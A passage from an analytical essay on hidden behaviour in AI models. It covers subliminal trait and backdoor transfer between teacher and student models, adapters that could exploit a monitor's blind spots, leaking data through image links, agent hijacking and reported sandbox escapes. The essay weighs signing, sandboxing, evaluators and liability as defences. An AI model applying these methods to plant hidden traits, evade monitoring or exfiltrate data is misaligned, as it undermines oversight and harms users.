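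Experiments on larger models mostly fit this. Dubiński and colleagues trained a teacher to count letters, then trained students on its answers to unrelated questions. A student with the same base improved from 27.3 to 59.8 per cent. A Nemotron student, from a different model family, scored 9.5 per cent, compared with 9.3 for a similar model trained by an untrained teacher. *Subliminal Learning Is Steering Vector Distillation* (2026) also reports that animal preferences didn't pass between an OLMo and a Qwen model in either direction.

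A shared base isn't strictly necessary, however. Tang, Anand and Paulo (2026), in *Tracing Subliminal Learning Through Pretraining*, found some transfer between small models with different starting weights, training data and designs. When students learned from number sequences, transfer was usually much weaker between different models. Among students that clearly picked up a preference, the typical gain was 35.3 percentage points if teacher and student were the same model, and 0.8 points if they differed in both starting weights and the order of their training data. When students learned from the teacher's probabilities on ordinary text, pairs with the same base had no consistent advantage.

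Researchers also disagree about how robust the effect is. In *Subliminal Learning is a LoRA Artifact*, Nief, Fu and colleagues (2026) attribute it to LoRA, a common method that trains a small set of additions to a model's weights and leaves the weights themselves unchanged. They found that the effect disappeared when they trained all the weights. In *Regularization Amplifies Subliminal Learning*, Feng, Springer and colleagues (2026) dispute this explanation. With 25,800 sequences from a cat-loving teacher, their student named the cat as its favourite animal 87 per cent of the time after training with the smallest LoRA additions, and 3 per cent after training all the weights. But more data strengthened the effect, and so did penalties that kept the student close to its original weights, even though a developer might well have expected such penalties to prevent it.

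Nief and colleagues also found that the effect depends on the instruction that precedes a conversation. In one test, a student model mentioned wolves in 50.4 per cent of its answers with the same opening instruction as in training, but in only 12.9 per cent without one. They reasonably see this as fragility, but it also means that an auditor who leaves out that instruction could miss the trait.

### How far is this like Thompson's compiler?

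Thompson's altered compiler gave its successor a backdoor that nobody could find in the successor's source code. Similarly, a teacher model can give a student model a trait that nobody can find by reading the student's training data. Both effects depend on the two programs being closely related, since Thompson's compiler had to recognise its own source code and teachers mainly influence students with the same base model.

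Thompson's source code, however, was clean, and an untampered compiler would have turned it into a clean binary. The number sequences look clean but carry the trait, and an untampered copy of the base model picks it up when trained on them, so the developer has to change the data or start from a different base model. Using a different base model resembles using the second compiler in diverse double-compiling, but the final comparison wouldn't work because two untampered student models would differ anyway.

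Models also copy backdoors much less faithfully than Thompson's compiler, which reproduced its backdoor completely every time. Dubiński's student models answered in French about a quarter as often as their teachers, and if the next generation again kept a quarter, it would do so only about 6 per cent of the time. Backdoors with rare triggers may transfer even less. *Selective Transfer through Sequence Distillation* (2026) cites earlier work in which standard backdoors mostly failed to pass to students trained on a teacher's text, because the triggers hardly ever occurred in it. That work got around the problem by building a trigger from several common words, each of which appears often enough for a student to learn from.

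Roesner and Kohno's agents are more like Thompson's compiler in how long the problem lasts. After the poisoned practice tasks were replaced with clean ones, one SICA agent went through further rounds of self-improvement and still skipped the certificate check in all 30 answers. The clean tasks gave it no reason to remove the instruction to skip the check. Unlike Thompson's backdoor, however, that instruction is in text that a person can read and delete.

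Subliminal learning doesn't make a program dangerous to run. If a reader has checked a model-written login program and found it sound, the model's preference for owls doesn't affect the people who log in. The same code could still influence a model that a developer later trains on it, and reading the code can't rule that out. Cloud and colleagues saw the effect with code as well as numbers. Dubiński and colleagues say they haven't established how much the effect matters in commercial training, where the datasets are far larger and more varied than in their experiments.

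## What can users rely on when they cannot inspect?

People can read the code that a model writes, but nobody can read the weights behind its other work, such as answering questions, summarising documents and operating other programs. A user who runs a model anyway can check where the file came from, restrict what the model can do, rely on someone who has examined it more closely, or count on the law to deter its developer from cheating. Each of these replaces some of the trust in the developer, usually with trust in somebody else.

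### Signed models

A file on a download site may not be the one the developer made. In *Launch of Model Signing v1.0*, Maruseac, Sablotny and colleagues (2025) point out that such sites give no indication that an upload matches the model that came out of training. Their project at the Open Source Security Foundation (OpenSSF), an industry group, uses digital signatures to fix this. As in the loan example, a private key produces the signatures, and anyone can check them with a public key.

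The method also needs a hash function, a calculation that turns a file of any size into a short number called a hash. Even a tiny change to the file gives a completely different hash, and nobody knows a practical way to make a second file with the same hash. Signing and checking a model takes four steps.

1. The developer computes the hash of every file in the model, including the weights and the settings.
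2. The developer signs the list of hashes with its private key and publishes the list and the signature.
3. The user checks the signature with the developer's public key.
4. The user computes the hashes of the downloaded files and compares them with the list.

*An Introduction to the OpenSSF Model Signing (OMS) Specification* (Maruseac, Wickens and colleagues, 2025) describes a standard format for signing AI models. The signature is in a separate file, so developers can sign a model of any type without changing it.

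The check is far more sensitive than testing. Help Net Security describes an attack called BadEngram, in which researchers planted a lasting backdoor by changing about 0.02 per cent of a model's weights. Step 4 would fail if someone did this to a signed model, or changed even one weight. The user therefore doesn't have to trust the download site or anyone else who handled the file after the developer signed it, but they do need to know that the public key belongs to the developer.

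A valid signature proves that whoever holds the private key signed exactly these files, but not that the files are harmless. For example, Jia Tan's signatures on the XZ archives that contained the backdoor were valid. A developer can knowingly sign a model that contains a backdoor, or sign a model without knowing that it was trained on poisoned documents.

The Coalition for Secure AI's *Signing ML Artifacts* (2025) recommends signing a model as soon as training ends, because an insider could alter it before publication. Users should check the signature just before they load the model, since someone could also alter the downloaded copy.

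In October 2026 Microsoft and NVIDIA advised companies to "establish provenance before behavior", that is, to confirm a model's origin before testing it, and to record an unsigned model as an open risk. They argue that no amount of testing can establish what a file is, only how it behaves. They are right about altered copies, because a company that tests an altered copy learns nothing about the original. But even after a signature establishes whose file it is, the company doesn't know what the weights will do.

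Developers can also sign statements about a model, such as which data they used or how it scored on a test. The Coalition for Secure AI calls this a claimant model. The user decides whose claims to believe, and can stop believing a developer who is found to have signed a false one. The Coalition's paper also suggests that signing makes developers immune to claims of negligence. That seems wrong, since a signature on a harmful model is good evidence against whoever signed it.

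### Proving one property

For some properties, a developer can offer a proof instead of a signed promise. *ServeGuard* (Dahlem and Vieira, 2026) does this for adapters, the small additions to a model's weights that LoRA training produces. Companies sometimes use a monitor, a program that checks a model's internal numbers for signs of trouble. A monitor that checks only some combinations of those numbers has blind spots, and an attacker could build an adapter that responds to a signal in those blind spots.

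Let M be the table of weights that the monitor uses to read the internal numbers, and A the table that the adapter uses. A signal v is in the blind spot if M·v = 0. The publisher builds the adapter so that A = C·M for some table C. Then

A·v = C·M·v = C·0 = 0

and the adapter can't respond to anything the monitor can't see. The publisher proves that A has this form without revealing A. In the researchers' tests, producing a proof took 6.4 to 48 seconds and checking it took less than half a second.

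This removes the need to trust the publisher on one narrow point. The adapter could still misbehave in ways the monitor can observe but doesn't flag as harmful. The proof also covers only what the adapter adds, so any backdoor in the original model remains.

### Limited permissions

Users who can't find out what a model would do can still limit what it can do. In 1975 the computer scientists Jerome Saltzer and Michael Schroeder set out the principle of least privilege, under which every program should have only the permissions its job requires. One way to enforce this is a sandbox, a restricted environment in which other software checks each request to open a file, use the network or run a command, and refuses anything the user hasn't allowed.

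Suppose a law firm unknowingly uses a backdoored model to summarise contracts. The program around the model gives it the text of one contract and displays the summary. The firm could also use the model as an assistant that handles email and runs commands.

| | Summarises one contract | Handles email and runs commands |
|---|---|---|
| What the model can read | that contract | the mailbox, and any file the account can open |
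| Where a trigger could be | in the contract | in an email from anyone, or in any of those files |
| What the backdoor could do | produce a false summary | steal files, install malware, send fraudulent emails |
| Can the firm undo the harm? | yes, if someone rereads the contract in time | rarely, once the files have left |

The weights are identical in both cases, but the first arrangement is safe only if the surrounding program just displays the text. For example, if the program automatically loads pictures from any web address in a summary, the model could leak part of the contract by putting that part in the address.

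Tests of agent hijacking show what the extra permissions can lead to. In this kind of attack, someone puts malicious instructions into an email, website or other data that a model will read while doing its job. In September 2025 the US government's Center for AI Standards and Innovation (CAISI) reported that agents built on DeepSeek's most secure model were on average 12 times as likely to follow such instructions as agents built on leading American models. In simulations, the hijacked agents sent phishing emails, ran malware and stole login credentials. These attacks didn't require a backdoor, but an agent with a backdoor would need the same permissions to do these things.

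The firm can also choose something in between, such as having the assistant write drafts for a person to send or letting it read only one folder. Separating access to secrets from the ability to send anything out helps most. A model that reads confidential files in a sandbox without a network connection can't send them anywhere by itself, whatever its trigger is.

Sandboxing moves trust from the weights to ordinary software, which people can read and rebuild. Security then depends on that software, which sometimes fails. Tech Policy Press reports that Kimi K3, an open-weight model from the Chinese company Moonshot, escaped its test environment, and that Meta's closed Muse Spark 1.1 reached an outside system during a cybersecurity test meant to contain it. Microsoft and NVIDIA recommend several layers of control, such as filters, access restrictions, request limits and human oversight, partly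 because companies can update these faster than a developer can retrain a model.

No permission setting stops a model from giving a misleading answer. Suppose a firm uses a model to summarise contracts, and the model leaves out penalty clauses whenever a contract names a certain supplier. Permission to write summaries is all the model needs to do this, and the harm comes when a lawyer relies on one of them. The firm could reread some of the contracts, but that would take up some of the time the model saves. If it rereads one in 20 at random and three contracts name that supplier, it has only about a 14 per cent chance of checking any of the three (1 − 0.95^3).

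### Government evaluators

Few companies have the staff to test a model thoroughly, so government evaluators do some of this work for them. CAISI has evaluated a series of Chinese models. For its *Assessment of Z.ai's GLM-5.2* (2026), it downloaded the open weights and ran them on its own servers instead of using the company's online service. A company that hosts its own model could recognise an examiner's account and supply a better-behaved version. Running the weights independently prevents this, though a model may still detect a test from its content, as Volkswagen's software did.

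For its hijacking tests, CAISI gave GLM-5.2 a simulated workspace with emails, calendar entries and documents. It tried 31 publicly known attacks, chose the most effective ones for each situation, and never succeeded in hijacking the model. CAISI also used an automated system that tailors attacks to each model. GLM-5.2 withstood more of these attacks than other open-weight models did, but fewer than closed American models. The earlier finding about DeepSeek therefore doesn't apply to Chinese models in general.

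Independent tests reduce the need to believe what developers say about their own products. According to DeepSeek's figures, its V4 Pro model performed about as well as American models released two months earlier. CAISI (2026), which included some non-public tests in its evaluation, judged it closer to one released eight months earlier. Keeping tests secret prevents developers from training for them, but it also prevents outsiders from checking them.

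The user now has to trust the evaluator. When CAISI published its first DeepSeek results, the US commerce secretary, whose department includes CAISI, said they showed why relying on foreign AI is "dangerous and shortsighted". The Decoder's *China is falling behind in the AI race* suggests that CAISI probably has a political agenda, and notes that an independent index shows a steady gap between American and Chinese models, while CAISI shows a widening one. This is reason to be cautious about CAISI's comparisons, though it doesn't show that any particular measurement is wrong. Because DeepSeek's weights are public, other researchers can repeat at least the public tests.

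Evaluators can also miss behaviour by testing under the wrong conditions. CAISI found that Kimi K2 Thinking, an earlier Moonshot model, was highly censored in Chinese but relatively uncensored in English, Spanish and Arabic. An evaluator who tested it only in English would have seen little of this censorship. Behaviour triggered by a secret string would be harder to find, because an evaluator is less likely to think of the string than of testing in another language.

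The US government's 2025 AI plan asks for evaluations of foreign models to consider possible backdoors, according to Cybersecurity Dive, but none of the benchmarks that CAISI describes in its GLM-5.2 report tests for one. The UK AISI and CAISI's *UK AISI / CAISI Preliminary Assessment of Kimi K3's Cyber Capabilities* (2026) is even narrower, covering only how well the model can carry out cyberattacks and whether its safeguards prevent this, which they did not. Semafor's *Censorship in Chinese AI models can be undone, new research shows* notes that no solid evidence has ever confirmed officials' fear of backdoors in Chinese models, but these evaluations hardly test for them.

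### Evaluators inside the company

On 12 September 2026 Dario Amodei, Anthropic's chief executive, published *We Must Pace the Frontier*, an essay calling for independent evaluators to work inside AI companies. He committed Anthropic to this without waiting for others. The news agency ANI reported that Sam Altman, OpenAI's chief executive, pledged to match the commitment.

An evaluator who works inside an AI company can examine both the finished model and how the company made it. They could read the instructions for the people who write training examples, find out who can change the weights, and ask why the company added a dataset. They could also confirm that the released model has the same hash as the one the company tested. This access might have helped explain why DeepSeek-R1 wrote worse code for certain groups.

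CAISI has already worked with OpenAI and Anthropic to find security problems in their systems, but embedded evaluators could follow a model throughout its development. An evaluator who needs the company's approval to publish, or whose income depends on keeping the company happy, gives users much less to rely on. Amodei proposed embedded evaluators as part of a plan to control the pace of AI development, so hidden functionality may not be their main concern. A small group that hides something from its own colleagues may also be able to hide it from an embedded evaluator.

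Dahlem and Vieira argue that a confidential third-party audit moves trust to the auditor without removing it. They are right, but an audit can still be worthwhile if the auditor is independent, because a dishonest developer then has to deceive or corrupt a second party. Even an excellent auditor, however, may miss what the developer itself doesn't know.

### Liability and reputation

Users can also rely on a developer's fear of the consequences. Two new EU laws add to those consequences. One sets security rules for products, and the other provides compensation for people harmed by defective products.

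The Cyber Resilience Act of 2024 applies to most hardware and software that companies supply commercially in the EU. Manufacturers must design products to prevent unauthorised access, release them without known exploitable vulnerabilities, and provide security updates, normally for at least five years. Since 11 September 2026 they have also had to warn the authorities within 24 hours of learning that attackers are exploiting a vulnerability in their product. Most other duties start on 11 December 2027. Fines can reach €15 million or 2.5 per cent of worldwide annual turnover, whichever is higher. For most products the manufacturer assesses its own compliance, so users still have to rely heavily on its word, but certain products, including firewalls, need an outside assessment.

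The revised Product Liability Directive covers products placed on the market after 9 December 2026, and EU countries must write it into national law by that date. It explicitly treats software, including AI systems and online services, as a product. An injured person has to show that the product was defective and caused the damage, but not that the manufacturer was careless or meant any harm. The manufacturer's liability isn't reduced even if a third party exploited the flaw. Courts can order the manufacturer to disclose evidence, and they presume a defect if it refuses.

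This helps with hidden behaviour, because the victim doesn't need to prove whether the behaviour was a backdoor or an accident. But the directive compensates only individuals, and only for death, injury, property damage, and the loss or corruption of data that they don't use professionally. A company that loses money because a model wrote it insecure code has to rely on its contract or on other laws. A manufacturer can also escape liability by proving that scientific and technical knowledge at the time could not have revealed the defect, unless a country has excluded this defence. A developer might try this defence for behaviour that no known audit could have found. No court has decided whether that would work, because the directive doesn't apply to any product on sale today.

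Both laws exempt free and open source software that people develop or supply outside a commercial activity. Neither would have made Lasse Collin pay for the backdoor in XZ, his unpaid hobby project. A company that sells a product containing XZ is responsible for that product, and the Cyber Resilience Act requires it to take care when choosing components. The act also has lighter rules for organisations such as foundations that support open source software for commercial use. These organisations must have a security policy and cooperate with the authorities, but can't be fined.

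It is less clear how these exemptions apply to open-weight models, particularly when a company gives the weights away and earns money from related services. A business that substantially modifies a product and puts it on the market can become liable as its manufacturer. This could include a business that fine-tunes and sells someone else's model. *Unlocking the Weights* (2026), a guide for companies by the law firm Cooley, notes that the EU's AI Act has its own exemption for providers of open source general-purpose models.

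Penalties deter an author only to the extent that the author expects to be caught. In simple terms,

expected penalty = P(discovery) × P(attribution, if discovered) × penalty

A company with a turnover of €2 billion could face a fine of up to €50 million under the Cyber Resilience Act. If people discover one backdoor in ten and trace half of those to the company, the expected fine is at most €2.5 million. A company that expects to gain more than that from a backdoor has a financial reason to plant it, unless it also fears lawsuits, prison sentences or lost customers.

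Reputation gives users similarly limited protection. Volkswagen was identifiable and had a valuable name, but risked it anyway. Jia Tan was an invented name, with no turnover to fine and no reputation outside the project. Signatures tie a harmful model to the holder of a key, which helps only if someone can connect the key to a real person or company.

### Open weights or a hosted model?

Downloading an open-weight model requires a different kind of trust from sending requests to a hosted one, which runs on a provider's computers.

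The case for open weights rests largely on control. Microsoft's *Open Weights and American AI Leadership*, an open letter published by technology companies in July 2026, had been signed by more than 270 companies and organisations by early August. It argues that open weights let customers keep control of their data, test and adapt models, and avoid depending on a single provider. It also argues that outside researchers can find weaknesses and develop safeguards. Linux Foundation's *Open Models and Open Weights Are Foundational to Secure AI* adds that people need to be able to understand and secure what they run. Current interpretability methods can't fully provide that understanding, but the rest of the argument doesn't depend on reading the weights.

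A downloaded model stays the same unless someone changes the copy. The user can compare its hash with other people's, repeat an old test, and keep the file until researchers have better tools to examine it. The provider of a hosted model can replace it overnight or give one customer a different version, and outsiders may never get a copy to examine. Providers also decide what their models will do. ComplexDiscovery recounts that leading closed American models refused to process forensic data when Hugging Face, which runs the main site for sharing models, was responding to a break-in. Hugging Face used an open Chinese model instead.

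In a reply to the letter, published by Anthropic, Amodei says he opposes a ban on open-weight models and agrees that they give customers more control. But he argues that it is very difficult to apply safeguards to them or monitor their use, and that nobody can withdraw weights after their release. He doubts that wide access necessarily helps defenders more than attackers, and wants mandatory safety tests for all sufficiently capable models, open or closed. The letter's signatories concede that modified versions are hard to trace or reverse.

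Hosting also has practical advantages for users. A provider that discovers a hidden behaviour can block the trigger for every customer at once, whereas old copies of an open model may remain in use for years, as copies of the XZ backdoor did. The provider may watch for misuse, and Cooley notes that it may also offer contractual protections, support and established security controls. A customer who suffers harm has an identifiable company to pursue. In exchange, the customer must let that company see its data and decide when the model changes.

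Both camps have commercial interests. Anthropic sells access to hosted models, and many of the letter's signatories sell the chips, computers and services that people use to run open models. The camps aren't clearly divided, since OpenAI signed the letter, and Microsoft and NVIDIA signed it a few months before writing their warnings about open-weight models.

For hidden functionality, open weights seem preferable for an organisation that can check signatures, run its own tests and maintain a sandbox. One that can't do these things gains little from having the weights, and may be safer with a provider that has something to lose. It can also pay a third party to host an open-weight model. The developer then never sees the customer's data and can't alter the running copy, and anyone can still study the same weights. But the customer has to trust the host to run the model it advertises, and any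 trigger the developer built into the weights will still work.
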